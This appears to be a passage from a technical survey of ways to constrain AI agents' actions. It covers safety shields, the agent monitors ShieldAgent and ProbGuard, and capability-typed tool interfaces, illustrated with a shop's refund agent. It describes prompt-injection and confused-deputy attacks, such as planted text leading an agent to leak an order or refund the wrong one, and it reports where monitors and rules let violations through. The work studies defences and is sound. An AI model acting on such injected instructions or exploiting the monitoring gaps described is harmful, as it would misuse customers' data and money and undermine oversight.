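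Kamath and colleagues also had Claude Sonnet 4.5 write the retail specification from the policy, the tool descriptions and a worked example. With Qwen3-8B as the agent, conformance was 100 percent and utility 42.1 percent, the same as with the handwritten version. But the one model-written rule that the paper prints, which covers reading a customer's profile, is weaker than the handwritten one. The handwritten rule requires an earlier lookup that returned the same customer's number. The model's rule, as printed, requires only that an earlier lookup succeeded, so an agent that had verified Ana could open Ben's profile. They describe both rules as correct, but they tested the model-written rules only on the ordinary retail tasks, which give a customer little reason to ask for somebody else's profile.

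Wang and colleagues found that when OpenAI's o1, a 2024 model, wrote AgentSpec rules, some were too narrow and others too broad. When told to protect critical configuration files, it sometimes covered only the files named in its examples. Its rule against unsafe pouring banned all pouring, including watering a houseplant. For driving in fog or rain, it applied the speed limit only in the fast lane. Its rules caught 87.3 percent of risky programs and prevented violations in five of eight driving scenarios, while the handwritten rules prevented them in all eight. For the robot, the paper reports 95.6 percent precision (the share of blocked cases that were truly hazardous) and 71.0 percent recall (the share of hazardous cases that were blocked). But it also describes 95.6 percent as the share of hazardous cases stopped, so it is unclear how many hazards got through.

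A solver can find contradictions between rules, and ActGov's search can find a rule that conflicts with a stated requirement, but neither can detect a requirement that nobody wrote down. The shop could look for such gaps by running example traces through each new rule, including traces the rule should refuse. A two-call trace in which Ana passes verification and the agent then requests Ben's profile would be enough to expose the gap in the model-written profile rule.

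## Shields that block steps leading to unavoidable violations

An agent can obey every rule and still reach a dead end, a state from which it can't avoid a later violation. The shop's two conflicting email rules caused a mild version of this, in which the monitors denied every call after the refund. This did little harm because the agent could stop. But when events continue without the agent, stopping doesn't help, and a monitor that checks one step at a time detects the problem too late. A shield blocks the earlier step that leads into the dead end.

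### A tank that overflows

Suppose a controller fills a tank that holds 10 units. An open valve adds 1 or 2 units per step, and the controller can't predict which. Nothing drains while the valve is open. Once opened, the valve stays open for at least three steps. The only rule is that the tank must not overflow.

At level 8, a one-step check allows the controller to open the valve, because the level after that step is at most 10. The valve then stays open for two more steps, and the level ends between 11 and 14. The next check may detect the danger, but only closing the valve would help, and the controller can't do that yet.

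A stricter check would require that at least one continuation complies with the rule, as Agent-C does for tool calls. This excludes level 8 but allows level 7, where the tank stays within its limit only if the valve adds 1 unit every time. A shield requires that the controller can comply whatever the valve adds:

| Condition for opening the valve | Highest level allowed | Worst level after three steps |
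|---|---|---|
| The next step can't overflow the tank | 8 | 14 |
| At least one continuation complies | 7 | 13 |
| The controller can comply whatever the valve adds | 4 | 10 |

The shield's caution has a cost. It refuses to open the valve at levels 5 to 7, although the tank might not have overflowed.

### Solving a game backwards

Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues (2017), in *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding*, showed how software can compute such limits from a rule and a model of the environment. They designed the method for reinforcement learning, in which a program learns by trial and error which actions earn rewards. The construction has four steps:

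1. Turn the rule into an automaton and mark the states that violate it. The rule must be a safety property.
2. Write a second automaton that describes which observations can follow each action. For the tank, it records that an open valve adds 1 or 2 units. It can leave out anything that doesn't affect the rule.
3. Combine the two automata into a game. Each state of the game pairs a state of the rule with a state of the environment. One player, the environment, picks any observation that the model allows, and the other, the system, picks an action. The system wins if it never reaches a violation.
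4. Work backwards from the violations to find the winning region, the set of states from which the system can always win.

The last step is a loop:

```
W₀    = all states that violate no rule
Wᵢ₊₁  = the states in Wᵢ with at least one action
        whose possible next states all lie in Wᵢ
```

The loop ends when a pass removes no states, and the remaining set W is the winning region. The shield permits an action only if every state the action could lead to is in W.

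For the tank, a state consists of the level and the number k of steps for which the valve must still stay open:

| Pass | States removed | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | k ≥ 1 and level 9 or 10 | Adding 2 overflows the tank |
| 2 | k ≥ 2 and level 7 or 8 | Adding 2 leads to a state removed in pass 1 |
| 3 | k = 3 and level 5 or 6 | Adding 2 leads to a state removed in pass 2 |
| 4 | none | |

In the winning region, the level is therefore at most 10 − 2k. Opening the valve sets k to 3, which gives the limit of 4.

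Alshiekh and colleagues use a larger tank as their own example. It holds 100 litres, may lose up to 1 litre per second, and must not overflow or run dry. The valve must keep its setting for three seconds after each change. The game has 602 states. The resulting shield forbids opening the valve above level 93 and forces it open when the level gets too low.

They prove that these shields prevent all violations if the environment behaves as modelled. They also prove that the shield interferes as little as possible, blocking an action only if some environment that fits the model could then cause a violation whatever the agent did next.

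### Offering safe actions or correcting a chosen one

A shield can act before or after the agent decides. A preemptive shield gives the agent a list of safe actions to choose from. A post-posed shield lets the agent choose freely and replaces the choice only if it is unsafe. This works even with an agent that has finished learning and has no information about the shield. In the basic version, the shield substitutes an arbitrary safe action. Alternatively, the agent can rank several actions, and the shield picks the highest-ranked safe one.

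A shield can offer a language model safe actions by hiding the forbidden tools, as far as a list of tool names can separate safe actions from unsafe ones. Correction is harder to apply to language models, because a shield that replaces a refused refund with an arbitrary safe action might send an email that nobody wanted. Returning an error and letting the model propose another call is closer to the ranked list.

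Alshiekh and colleagues tested shields on a robot in two grid worlds, a simulated car, the Atari game Seaquest and the water tank. The shielded car never crashed, while the unshielded one was still crashing at the end of training. In Seaquest, the shield prevented all violations of two rules about when a submarine must surface, and the learner's performance did not change. In most of the other tests, shielded agents learned faster. In the larger grid world, the robot found the best route only when it gave the shield three ranked actions and received no penalty for unsafe ones. Each shield with a reported computing time took two seconds or less to compute.

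An agent that trains with a shield may still need it after training. In *Online Shielding for Reinforcement Learning* (2022), Könighofer, Rudolf and colleagues trained agents to play a two-player version of the game Snake. Shielding improved performance during training, but in most experiments the shielded agents learned less safe behaviour than agents trained without a shield. This happened even when the shielded agents received penalties for blocked actions.

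### When the model is wrong

The guarantee holds only if the model covers everything the environment can do. If the valve sometimes added 3 units, opening it at level 4 could bring the tank to 13. In Alshiekh and colleagues' construction, an observation that the model excludes counts as a win for the system, and from then on the shield permits every action. An operator should therefore treat such an observation as an alarm.

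A more cautious model makes the shield more restrictive. If the valve could add up to 3 units per step, the shield would allow the controller to open it only at level 1 or below. If the valve could add up to 4, the shield would never allow the controller to open it, because even an empty tank could reach 12. The shield also needs correct readings and a safe starting point, since it can't prevent a violation if the tank starts at level 8 with a newly opened valve.

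Large models are also a practical problem because, according to Könighofer and colleagues, the computation needed to analyse every combination of state and action in advance grows exponentially with the dimensions of the problem. Their shield instead analyses the next k steps while the agent is on its way to its next decision. They give no upper limit on how long this takes, so the agent must be able to wait.

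A shield that looks only k steps ahead can still allow a step into a dead end, where a violation is unavoidable. In the tank, a two-step check would allow the controller to open the valve at level 6, because the level could reach only 10 in two steps. The third step could then bring it to 12. Könighofer and colleagues recommend making k larger than the number of steps between neighbouring decisions.

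### Shields that accept some risk

If every useful action carries a tiny risk, a shield that allows no risk blocks them all. Probabilistic shields allow a limited risk. They use a Markov decision process, a model that gives the probability of each possible result of an action.

Heck, Macák and colleagues (2026), in *Shields to Guarantee Probabilistic Safety in MDPs*, analyse a common type, the δ-shield, which Jansen and colleagues had introduced earlier. Let V(s) be the lowest achievable probability of ever reaching a bad state from state s. Let Q(s, a) be that probability if the agent takes action a now and acts as safely as possible afterwards. The shield allows a if

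```
δ · Q(s, a) ≤ V(s)
```

where δ is a number between 0 and 1. With δ = 0.5, the agent may take actions up to twice as risky as the safest one. If the safest action carries no risk, the formula forbids all risk, so Heck and colleagues also test a version that limits the difference between the two probabilities instead of their ratio. Könighofer and colleagues likewise set their threshold relative to the safest action, which ensures that the shield always allows at least one action.

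A limit on each step doesn't limit the risk of the whole run. In an example from Heck and colleagues, an agent passes three points, each with a 10 percent risk of reaching a bad state. It can avoid the first two risks but not the third. At each of the first two points, the lowest achievable risk is V = 0.1, while taking the risky action raises it to at least Q = 0.1 + 0.9 × 0.1 = 0.19. A shield with δ = 0.5 allows both risky actions, because 0.5 × 0.19 is less than 0.1. If the agent takes both, its total risk is 1 − 0.9³ = 27.1 percent, although it could have kept the risk to 10 percent.

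The same effect occurs in the tank over a longer run. Suppose the valve adds 1 or 2 units with equal probability. If the controller opens it at level 5, the tank overflows only if the valve adds 2 units three times in a row, which has a one in eight chance. A shield that allowed this risk once would allow it every time the tank drained back to level 5. Over six openings, the probability of at least one overflow would be 1 − (7/8)⁶, or about 55 percent.

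### Why no shield can use the whole risk budget

An ideal shield would keep the total risk below a limit and never interfere with an agent that stays below it on its own. Heck and colleagues prove that no shield can do both in every case if the limit lies strictly between 0 and 100 percent. To illustrate their proof, suppose the limit is 50 percent and a fair coin decides which of two situations the agent faces. In each situation, the agent can choose a harmless action or one that is certain to cause a violation.

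An agent that would choose the harmful action only after heads, or only after tails, has a total risk of 50 percent, so the shield should allow it. But a shield that allows the action after both heads and tails also allows an agent that always chooses it, whose risk is 100 percent. After heads, the shield can't observe what the agent would have done after tails. Information-flow rules cause a similar difficulty because they also depend on runs that the monitor never observes.

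Two of Heck and colleagues' shields make opposite assumptions about those other runs. The pessimistic shield assumes that the agent takes the greatest possible risks in them. It keeps the total risk within the limit, but in the tests it allowed hardly more than a shield that accepts no risk. The optimistic shield assumes that the agent behaves as safely as possible in the other runs, and intervenes only once the risks taken in the current run exceed the budget. It never interferes with a safe agent, but it can let an unsafe one exceed the limit.

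A third method divides the budget in advance. It starts with a shield that permits only the safest actions and records the choices agents try to make. It then permits additional choices one at a time, but only if the worst permitted behaviour still keeps the total risk below the limit. In the coin example, it could permit the harmful action after heads or after tails, depending on which it added first.

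The shield can add choices between runs, but adding them during a run can break the guarantee. If it updated after the coin toss, it would permit one harmful action after heads and the other after tails. Either update is safe by itself, but together they would let an agent cause a violation after every toss.

Heck and colleagues tested the shields on small simulated tasks with known probabilities. In a power-management task with a 20 percent limit, an agent that ignored safety had these results:

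| Shield | Risk of a bad outcome | Share of actions allowed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 47.9% | 100% |
| Safest actions only | 0% | 77.1% |
| Limit on the extra risk at each step | 47.9% | nearly all |
| Budget shared out between runs | 6.2% | 87.0% |

There was no gain in a small corridor task with a 5 percent limit, where the last method and the strictest shield both allowed this type of agent only 2 percent of its actions. The guarantee depends on the model's probabilities being correct.

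### Rules that change during a run

Corsi, Mallik and colleagues (2025), in *Efficient Dynamic Shielding for Parametric Safety Specifications*, built shields for a robot that detects obstacles only when it gets close to them. Each new obstacle adds a rule. Their coarsest version divided the visible area into 400 cells, any of which might contain an obstacle. A separate shield for every combination of occupied cells would require 2⁴⁰⁰ computations.

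They instead compute one shield per cell in advance and combine the relevant ones during the run. The combined shield first keeps only the actions that all the individual shields allow. It then removes any state that has no actions left, along with the actions that might lead there, and repeats this until nothing changes. With the shop's conflicting email rules, this removal would make the combined shield block the refund.

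Preparing the individual shields took 3 to 19 minutes, depending on cell size. In 70 random navigation tasks per cell size, combining the shields took between a fraction of a second and a few seconds per step on average. This was up to five times faster than computing a new shield from scratch.

A new rule can also arrive when the agent is in a state where the new shield has no safe action. To prevent this, Corsi and colleagues treat everything outside the robot's visible area as an obstacle. If the new shield can't yet take over, the old one stays in force and keeps the robot inside the area it has already checked. This works only because the obstacles don't move. The robot also sometimes got stuck.

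An agent's permissions, by contrast, can change during a task. Suppose the shop's manager bans all emails just after the agent has refunded Ana and before it has written to her. If the old shield stayed in force, the agent would send her a forbidden email, but if the new one took over at once, she would get no confirmation. The shop would have to decide in advance which new rules take effect immediately and which wait until the agent finishes its current task.

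### The missing model of email and websites

Alshiekh and colleagues say the main drawback of shields is that they need a model of the environment. A tank can be modeled with a few numbers, but nobody has a comparably small and reliable model of an inbox, a website or a file system. A web page can contain any text, other people can change a file between two calls, and an attacker may choose what the agent reads. Allowing for all of this would be like allowing for the valve that might add 4 units, and the shield would refuse almost everything. A narrower model would permit more, but its guarantee would fail whenever something happened that the developer had left out.

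The shop's agent must email a customer within five calls of a refund, but the mail service may sometimes fail. If it never fails more than twice in a row, a shield can allow the refund, then two other calls, and after that only the email until it goes through. If the service can fail any number of times, the shield must block every refund, because it can't guarantee that the email will go through in time. To choose the right shield, the shop needs to know how many times in a row the mail service can fail, which it can't work out from its own rules.

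Shields suit language-model agents better when the rules concern only the order of the agent's own calls, because the rules then provide the whole model. The conflicting email rules are an example. A developer could also model a few results for each tool, such as a refund that succeeds, fails or gets no reply, and compute a shield for that part of the system.

### ShieldAgent

Some systems for language-model agents use the idea of a shield more loosely. *ShieldAgent* (Chen, Kang and Li, 2025) uses GPT-4o, a 2024 model, to extract rules from policy documents and translate them into temporal logic. Before a web agent takes each action, ShieldAgent gathers the rules for that type of action, uses language models and other tools to determine which conditions are true, and runs code that checks each rule.

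The final decision depends on a weight θ for each rule, which the system learns from examples. Acting and not acting each receive a score:

```
P = exp(sum of θ over the rules that hold) / Z
allow the action if  P(act) − P(don't act) ≥ ε
```

Here Z normalises the scores, and ε is a threshold the operator chooses. Suppose an action breaks one rule with a weight of 0.1 and not acting breaks none. If Z makes the two scores add up to 1, acting scores about 0.475 and not acting about 0.525, a difference of −0.05. With a threshold of −0.1, ShieldAgent would allow the action despite correctly detecting the violation. Chen and colleagues use weights because some extracted rules may be wrong, and enforcing all of them strictly could cause many false alarms.

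ShieldAgent states that the condition "guarantees the safety of the action sequence". But the condition compares acting with not acting at the current step, and does not check whether a safe continuation exists. At level 8, opening the tank's valve breaks no rule yet, so ShieldAgent could allow it unless the rules already included the limit of 4.

The tests measured how well ShieldAgent classifies actions. Chen and colleagues collected runs of a web agent in six simulated environments, including an online shop and a code-hosting site, and attacked the agent to produce unsafe runs. ShieldAgent classified about 91 percent of runs correctly and falsely flagged 4.8 percent of safe runs. GPT-4o with the full policy in its prompt classified about 75 percent correctly.

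In a live test, ShieldAgent checked each step and gave the agent feedback. Among the tasks the agent completed, the share that complied with the policy rose from 46.8 to 65.3 percent in the online shop and from 22.8 to 50.7 percent on the code-hosting site.

### Pro2Guard

Pro2Guard, which its developers have renamed ProbGuard, does estimate what will happen later in a run. Wang, Poskitt and colleagues (2025), in *ProbGuard*, illustrate it with a household robot that must not leave the kitchen for more than ten minutes while the stove is on. The system describes each state by a few true-or-false conditions, such as whether the stove is on and whether the robot is in the kitchen. From recorded runs, it estimates the probability of moving from state i to state j:

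```
P(j | i) = (nᵢⱼ + 1) / (nᵢ + kᵢ)
```

Here nᵢⱼ is the number of recorded moves from i to j, nᵢ is the number of all recorded moves from i, and kᵢ is the number of states that can follow i. Adding 1 gives a small probability to possible moves that never occurred in the recordings. The result is a Markov chain, a model in which the next state depends only on the current one. ProbGuard uses the chain to compute the probability that the run will stay safe, and intervenes if that probability falls below a threshold θ.

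This differs from a shield because the Markov chain describes what the agent usually does, while a winning region shows whether the agent could still avoid a violation, regardless of its usual behaviour. If a prompt injection changes that behaviour, recordings of normal runs may poorly predict what the agent will do next.

Wang, Poskitt and colleagues give a statistical guarantee that, with enough recorded runs, the estimate lies within a chosen distance of the true probability at a chosen confidence level. They calculate that the household tasks need between 530 and 100,000 runs for an error of at most 10 percentage points with 95 percent confidence. They used 30 runs per task, so the guarantee doesn't apply to the monitors they tested. The guarantee also assumes that the chosen conditions capture everything in the history that affects the future.

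ProbGuard's driving test used Apollo, a driving system that contains no language model. ProbGuard gave a warning before the violation in all seven scenarios. The longest warning came 38.66 seconds ahead, but at that threshold, θ = 0.7, the monitor also raised an alarm in every safe run. At θ = 0.3 it raised no false alarms and warned between 0.01 and 15.84 seconds ahead, though 0.01 seconds is too short to prevent the violation.

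The household test used SafeAgentBench, a set of simulated tasks, with GPT-4o mini as the agent. ProbGuard either stopped the run or added a warning to the agent's prompt:

| Intervention | Threshold θ | Unsafe runs | Completed tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | none | 40.6% | 59.4% |
| Stop the run | 0.9 | 2.6% | 10.4% |
| Stop the run | 0.5 | 21.4% | 41.1% |
| Warn the agent | 0.9 | 14.1% | 47.7% |

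Warning the agent at θ = 0.9 led to fewer unsafe runs and more completed tasks than stopping it at θ = 0.5. But the model can ignore a warning. Stopping the run prevents further actions but may not prevent the violation, because if the robot stops outside the kitchen, the stove stays on.

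## Tool interfaces typed by capability

State machines, formulas and shields keep the permitted sequence of actions in a rule that is separate from the tools. A developer can instead build the sequence into the tools' arguments. Suppose `issue_refund` accepts only a value of type `VerifiedOrder`, and the agent can get such a value only by verifying the customer and then reading one of that customer's orders. A program that tries to issue a refund first has no `VerifiedOrder` to pass to `issue_refund`, so it is rejected by the type checker, the part of a compiler that tests whether each function receives the right kind of value.

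### Signatures for the shop's tools

A function's signature gives the types of its arguments and of its result. The shop could use these:

```
verify_customer(Text, Text)          → Customer or NoMatch
read_order(Customer, OrderNumber)    → VerifiedOrder or NotFound
issue_refund(VerifiedOrder, Amount)  → Refunded or Declined
send_email(Customer, Text)           → Sent
```

Only the shop's own code can create a `Customer` or a `VerifiedOrder`. The agent's program can store these values and pass them on, but it can't build one. The type checker accepts this program:

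```
1  customer = verify_customer("ana@example.com", "N1 7AA")
2  if customer is NoMatch: stop
3  order = read_order(customer, 1042)
4  if order is NotFound: stop
5  issue_refund(order, £60)
6  send_email(customer, "We have refunded £60.")
```

The checker goes through the lines without running them. After line 2, `customer` must be a `Customer`, because otherwise the program would have stopped, so line 3 is allowed. After line 4, `order` must be a `VerifiedOrder`, so line 5 is allowed too. The checker rejects the next program:

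```
1  issue_refund(1042, £60)
2  customer = verify_customer("ana@example.com", "N1 7AA")
```

Line 1 passes an order number where the function requires a `VerifiedOrder`, so neither line runs. Swapping the lines would not help, because 1042 would still be a number. The checker also stops the leaked order, because "claims@example.net" is text and `send_email` requires a `Customer`. To let the agent email couriers, the shop would have to add another function.

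Some checks still have to happen when the tools run, because the type checker can't determine whether Ana's postcode will match, who owns order 1042 or what it cost. `read_order` looks up the owner before it returns anything, so the agent never receives the details of Ben's order. `issue_refund` compares the amount with the price stored in the `VerifiedOrder`. The types prevent any program from issuing a refund without going through these checks.

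### Capabilities, typestate and session types

A `VerifiedOrder` is a capability, an unforgeable reference that names a resource and grants the right to use it. Dennis and Van Horn introduced capabilities in 1966 (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026, *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*). In their design, the operating system keeps a list of capabilities for each computation. Each entry points to a resource and specifies what the program may do with it, and the program refers to an entry by its position in the list.

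Hardy explained in *The Confused Deputy* (1988) why a resource's name and the right to use it belong together. At the computing company Tymshare, a compiler had permission to write files in its own directory, where it recorded usage statistics. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user gave the name of the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. Because the compiler was allowed to write there, the operating system let it overwrite the billing records. The compiler had authority from two sources, the user and its own licence, and no way to indicate which one it was using. If users had been required to supply a capability for the output file instead of a name, this user could not have supplied one for the billing file.

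The leaked order follows the same pattern, because the agent served the attacker's purpose by using the shop's authority to email anyone. Text in a delivery note can include an email address but not a `Customer` value.

Typestate lets the operations permitted on a value change as the program runs. Strom and Yemini (1986), in *Typestate*, distinguished the operations that a value's type permits in general from the subset permitted in a particular context. For example, a program may read a file while it is open but not after closing it. Strom had earlier presented the idea as a security mechanism in *Mechanisms for Compile-Time Enforcement of Security*, in which a compiler checks the sequence of operations on each variable along every path through the program. In effect, each value has its own small state machine. An order could start as refundable and become refunded, and the compiler would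 reject `issue_refund` for a refunded order.

Session types describe a whole exchange between two parties. Honda (1993), in *Types for Dyadic Interaction*, defined types for sending, receiving, doing one thing after another, and choosing between alternatives. Every type has a matching co-type for the other party. In simplified notation, a refund request would have these two types:

```
shop:             send Refund;     be ready for Paid or Declined
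payment service:  receive Refund;  choose Paid or Declined
```

A shop-side program that handled only `Paid` would fail the check. `VerifiedOrder` only requires certain earlier steps, whereas a session type can also require later ones.

### A refund that works only once

The signatures above don't stop the double refund, because a program can pass the same `order` to `issue_refund` twice. The shop can prevent this by making `VerifiedOrder` a type whose values can be used only once, which programming-language researchers call a linear or affine type. The first refund then uses up `order`, and the checker rejects any later line that mentions it. `read_order` would return the order's description separately, so the agent could still refer to the order in an email.

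A single-use value can't be copied, which prevents the duplicate references that typestate alone allows. If the variables `a` and `b` both refer to order 1042 and the program refunds `a`, a checker that doesn't detect that they refer to the same order will still treat `b` as refundable. Kellogg, Shadab and colleagues (2022) call the need to reason about duplicate references a key barrier to checkers that miss no violations, which they note are rarely deployed.

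Single-use values can also separate a declined payment from a lost reply:

```
issue_refund(VerifiedOrder, Amount)
    → Refunded
    or Declined, with a new VerifiedOrder
    or NoReply
```

The agent has a new value after a decline and can try again, but it has none after a lost reply, so it can't pay Ana twice. Praetor's learned state machine permitted a retry in both cases, while the Agent-C rule against two refunds would have blocked both retries.

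However, the agent could call `read_order` again and get another `VerifiedOrder` for the same order. The type limits how often a program can use one value, but not how many values the shop issues. `read_order` therefore has to check a stored record and refuse to issue a new value once a refund request has been sent, even in a later conversation.

### Why the model should not hold the handle

Most agents propose one tool call at a time, and they do so in text, so they can't hold a `VerifiedOrder` at all. The application can store the real values in a table and give the model only labels for them:

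| Label | Type | Contents | Status |
|---|---|---|---|
| `customer-a` | `Customer` | customer 17, ana@example.com | reusable |
| `order-a` | `VerifiedOrder` | order 1042, £60, customer 17 | unused |

The application checks types at runtime, on each call. When the model requests `issue_refund("order-a", £60)`, the application looks up the label `order-a`, checks that it refers to an unused `VerifiedOrder`, marks it as used and then sends the payment request. If the model invents the label `order-b`, the lookup fails.

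The label `order-a` is a string, like an order number, but it has an effect only in this conversation, and only because the application added it to the table after a successful check. Text from an attacker can't add a row. The order number 1042 names the same order for everybody, and anyone can write it down, so a separate rule has to decide who may use it. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) calls the property that order numbers lack "No Designation Without Authority". A long random code could replace the table and would be hard to guess, but an attacker might persuade the agent to email it to somebody who could then use it.

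Keeping the table outside the model also makes it easy to withdraw a permission, because the application can delete its row. Miller and colleagues describe the same approach for capabilities in general. The owner of a resource hands out access to a forwarder instead of the resource itself, and later turns the forwarder off.

Handles don't prevent every confused-deputy attack. If Ana has two open orders, the table contains two valid labels, and a planted instruction could still cause the agent to refund the wrong order.

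### Checking a program before it runs

Some agents write a short program that makes several tool calls, and a compiler can check the whole program before any of it takes effect. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) gives an example in which a model has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new number. The model writes code that subtracts the 50 but returns a sentence instead of a number. The compiler rejects the code before it runs, so the balance stays at 100. If the error had surfaced only when the program ran, the subtraction would already have happened.

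A rejected program is sure to have no effect, but one that passes can still stop halfway, for example if the mail service fails after the refund. A check on each call can use the actual values and works with ordinary tool calling, but it lets the early steps of a plan run even when it will refuse the last one. The two methods work well together because a compiler can ensure that the program goes through the runtime checks.

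An agent often can't write its whole program in advance, because the next step depends on what it reads. LACUNA therefore lets the program call the model again partway through, and the compiler checks each new piece of code in the place where it will run.

The guarantee also requires a language that doesn't let programs bypass the type system. Many languages let a program relabel a value as another type or find hidden functions by name at runtime. Odersky and colleagues compile agents' code in a "safe mode" of the programming language Scala that forbids both.

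It also matters who writes the properties the checker tests. In *VeriGuard* (2025), the model writes both the code for an action and the conditions that a verifier checks it against, so the conditions may also be wrong. In the shop, a developer writes the signatures and the model can't change them.

### Tracked capabilities in Scala

Martin Odersky, who designed Scala, leads a group at the Swiss university EPFL that has built two such systems. The earlier one, TACIT, is a server that existing agents can connect to. The agent sends it Scala code as an ordinary tool call, and the server runs the code only if it compiles.

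TACIT relies on capture checking, an experimental Scala feature that records in a value's type which capabilities the value can use. If a function writes to file `f`, its type includes `f`. This has two main uses:

- **Temporary access.** A program can request access to a folder for the duration of one block of code. If the block tries to return a function that could still read the folder afterwards, the function's type reveals this and the compiler rejects it.
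- **Secrets.** Confidential files arrive in a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent can apply a function to the contents only if the function's type includes no capabilities, so the function can't print, save or send anything. The result stays in the wrapper. A trusted local model can summarise a secret report for the user without the agent's own model ever receiving the text.

Odersky and colleagues tested this on a software project with a folder of secrets. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections and added 11 requests in which the user tried to extract secrets directly. The table gives the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output:

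| Model and threat | Secrets as plain text | Secrets in `Classified` |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, malicious users | 81.8% | 100% |
| MiniMax M2.5, injections | 97.5% | 100% |
| MiniMax M2.5, malicious users | 27.3% | 100% |

Claude already resisted every injection, so the wrapper made a difference only when the user asked for the secrets. With the wrapper, utility on the ordinary tasks rose from 83.3 to 99.2 percent for Claude and from 88.3 to 90.0 percent for MiniMax, although the researchers suspect that time limits lowered Claude's unprotected score.

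They also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, which counted one successful attack in 1,926 trials. In that trial, the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews that contained the attacker's recommendation of another. With OpenAI's o4-mini, TACIT completed fewer tasks in all four domains than CaMeL, a system that labels data values, although the paper describes their utility as comparable. On office tasks, TACIT completed 52.9 percent, compared with 81.4 percent for CaMeL.

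Three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher on τ²-bench when they wrote typed Scala than when they used ordinary tool calls. The compiler rejected at most 8 percent of their code. But the airline interface in this test included `cancelReservation(reservationId: String)`, which accepts any text, so an agent could cancel a reservation without looking it up or checking its owner. The result therefore shows that models can write typed code, but not how utility changes when the types enforce the order of actions.

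LACUNA, the group's later system, did worse on the same benchmark. DeepSeek-v4-flash solved 76.0 percent of 392 tasks with LACUNA and 90.0 percent with ordinary tool calls. On retail tasks, the figures were 58.8 and 80.9 percent. In the abstract, Zhao and colleagues call the overall result "on par with the baseline agent", despite the 14-point gap. The compiler rejected 22.4 percent of the model's retail code. They expect better prompts or extra training to help.

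### ELBA and the hidden constructor

The closest published match to `VerifiedOrder` is in *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026). In the paper's system, ELBA, agents write programs in Haskell, whose types show what side effects a program can have. One agent compiles bibliographies and may use only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that writes to the bibliography accepts only a `Trusted` entry, and only the function that fetches entries from DBLP can create one. The agent can sort and filter entries freely, but it can't add an invented entry to the bibliography.

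Across 100 bibliography tasks with Claude Sonnet 5, none of ELBA's 925 citations were false, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent with a web search tool. This supports the basic pattern, though less than 2 percent of the ordinary agent's citations were false.

Zhou and colleagues also tested ELBA on AgentDojo's tasks for the messaging service Slack, using stricter rules that limit what an agent may do after it reads untrusted data. All four models resisted all the attacks even without these rules. The researchers then simulated a worst case by replacing the instructions of any sub-agent that read an injection with the attacker's text:

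| Model | Attacks that succeeded, without rules → with rules | Tasks completed, without rules → with rules |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 42.2% → 0% | 71.2% → 47.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 37.4% → 0% | 75.8% → 42.4% |
| GPT-5.4 | 15.5% → 0% | 75.9% → 46.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 26.5% → 0% | 67.2% → 40.0% |

The rules held even when the attacker fully controlled the model, but the agents' task completion rate was 23 to 33 percentage points lower. Difficulty writing valid Haskell did not cause the drop, since the models needed only 0.13 retries per run on average, and only 7 of 2,688 runs ended because the model could not produce code that passed.

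ELBA doesn't have single-use values, so for now a shop using it would have to track at runtime which refund authorizations have been used. Zhou and colleagues suggest linear types as a future way to provide "one-shot authorizations".

### Dividing authority among several agents

An agent can hand part of its work to another agent and pass on only the handles that work requires. In ELBA, a sub-agent works under the same types as its parent or stricter ones, and the parent can't loosen them. For example, the shop's agent could give a `Customer` but no `VerifiedOrder` to a sub-agent that writes emails.

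Without such limits, one agent can become another's confused deputy. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes attacks in which an untrusted agent sends instructions to an agent with more privileges. The paper's defence, SEAGENT, labels each agent, tool and database, records the path by which a request arrived and applies central rules to that path. It doesn't use capabilities. In the paper's tests, SEAGENT stopped every attack.

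Handles can't enforce a limit that several agents share. *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (Sterling, 2026) gives the example of a $100,000 budget from which one agent may spend $45,000 and another $60,000. Each payment is valid, but together they exceed the budget. In Sterling's architecture, each agent receives only the part of the system's state that its role requires and can only propose changes. A central component with access to the whole state runs a fixed list of checks on each proposal, accepts or refuses it, and logs the decision. Sterling proves that the stated limits hold whatever the agents propose, but notes that the system will enforce a badly specified limit as written.

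### Undeserved refunds, coarse types and unwrapped tools

A `VerifiedOrder` proves that the customer passed verification and owns the order. It doesn't show that the goods were faulty, that Ana asked for a refund or that £60 is a fair amount. The agent could refund every order it reads, and each program would pass the type check. The shop could add a type such as `ApprovedReturn`, which only the returns department's software can create, but then a person or another program has to decide whether to approve each return.

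A type that is too broad lets an agent do more than its task requires. If `verify_customer` returned a general `Verified` value and `issue_refund` accepted it with any order number, an agent that had verified Ana could refund Ben's orders. The compiler would not report an error, just as it accepts any text in `cancelReservation`. Similarly, a file capability for a whole disk gives too much access to an agent that needs one folder. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) extends Scala's checker so that a developer can exclude a whole kind of capability without listing each one, but the developer still has to decide what each task needs.

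Existing tools also need wrappers, since most accept plain text and numbers. TACIT's shared library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each τ²-bench domain took a few hundred more. Those wrappers took little work to write because they copied the existing tool descriptions one for one, but for the same reason they accept any reservation number. To build an interface that enforces order, somebody has to work out which call should produce the evidence that another call requires. The checking itself is fast. TACIT compiles a typical piece of code in under a second, and *What's in the Box* (2025) found that capture checking took less than 15 percent of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library.

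Few developers have taken this approach. *When Code Becomes an LLM Call* (2026) examined how agent software constrains its calls to language models. Of the constraints developers had implemented, 70.5 percent were ordinary code checks and 7.6 percent were limits on the model's capabilities.

The shop also has to trust the wrappers. If a bug makes `read_order` skip the ownership check, the function will issue a valid `VerifiedOrder` for somebody else's purchase. The agent can also bypass verification if the old `issue_refund`, which takes an order number, remains available under another name.

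## Workflow graphs fixed in advance, and tasks that do not fit them

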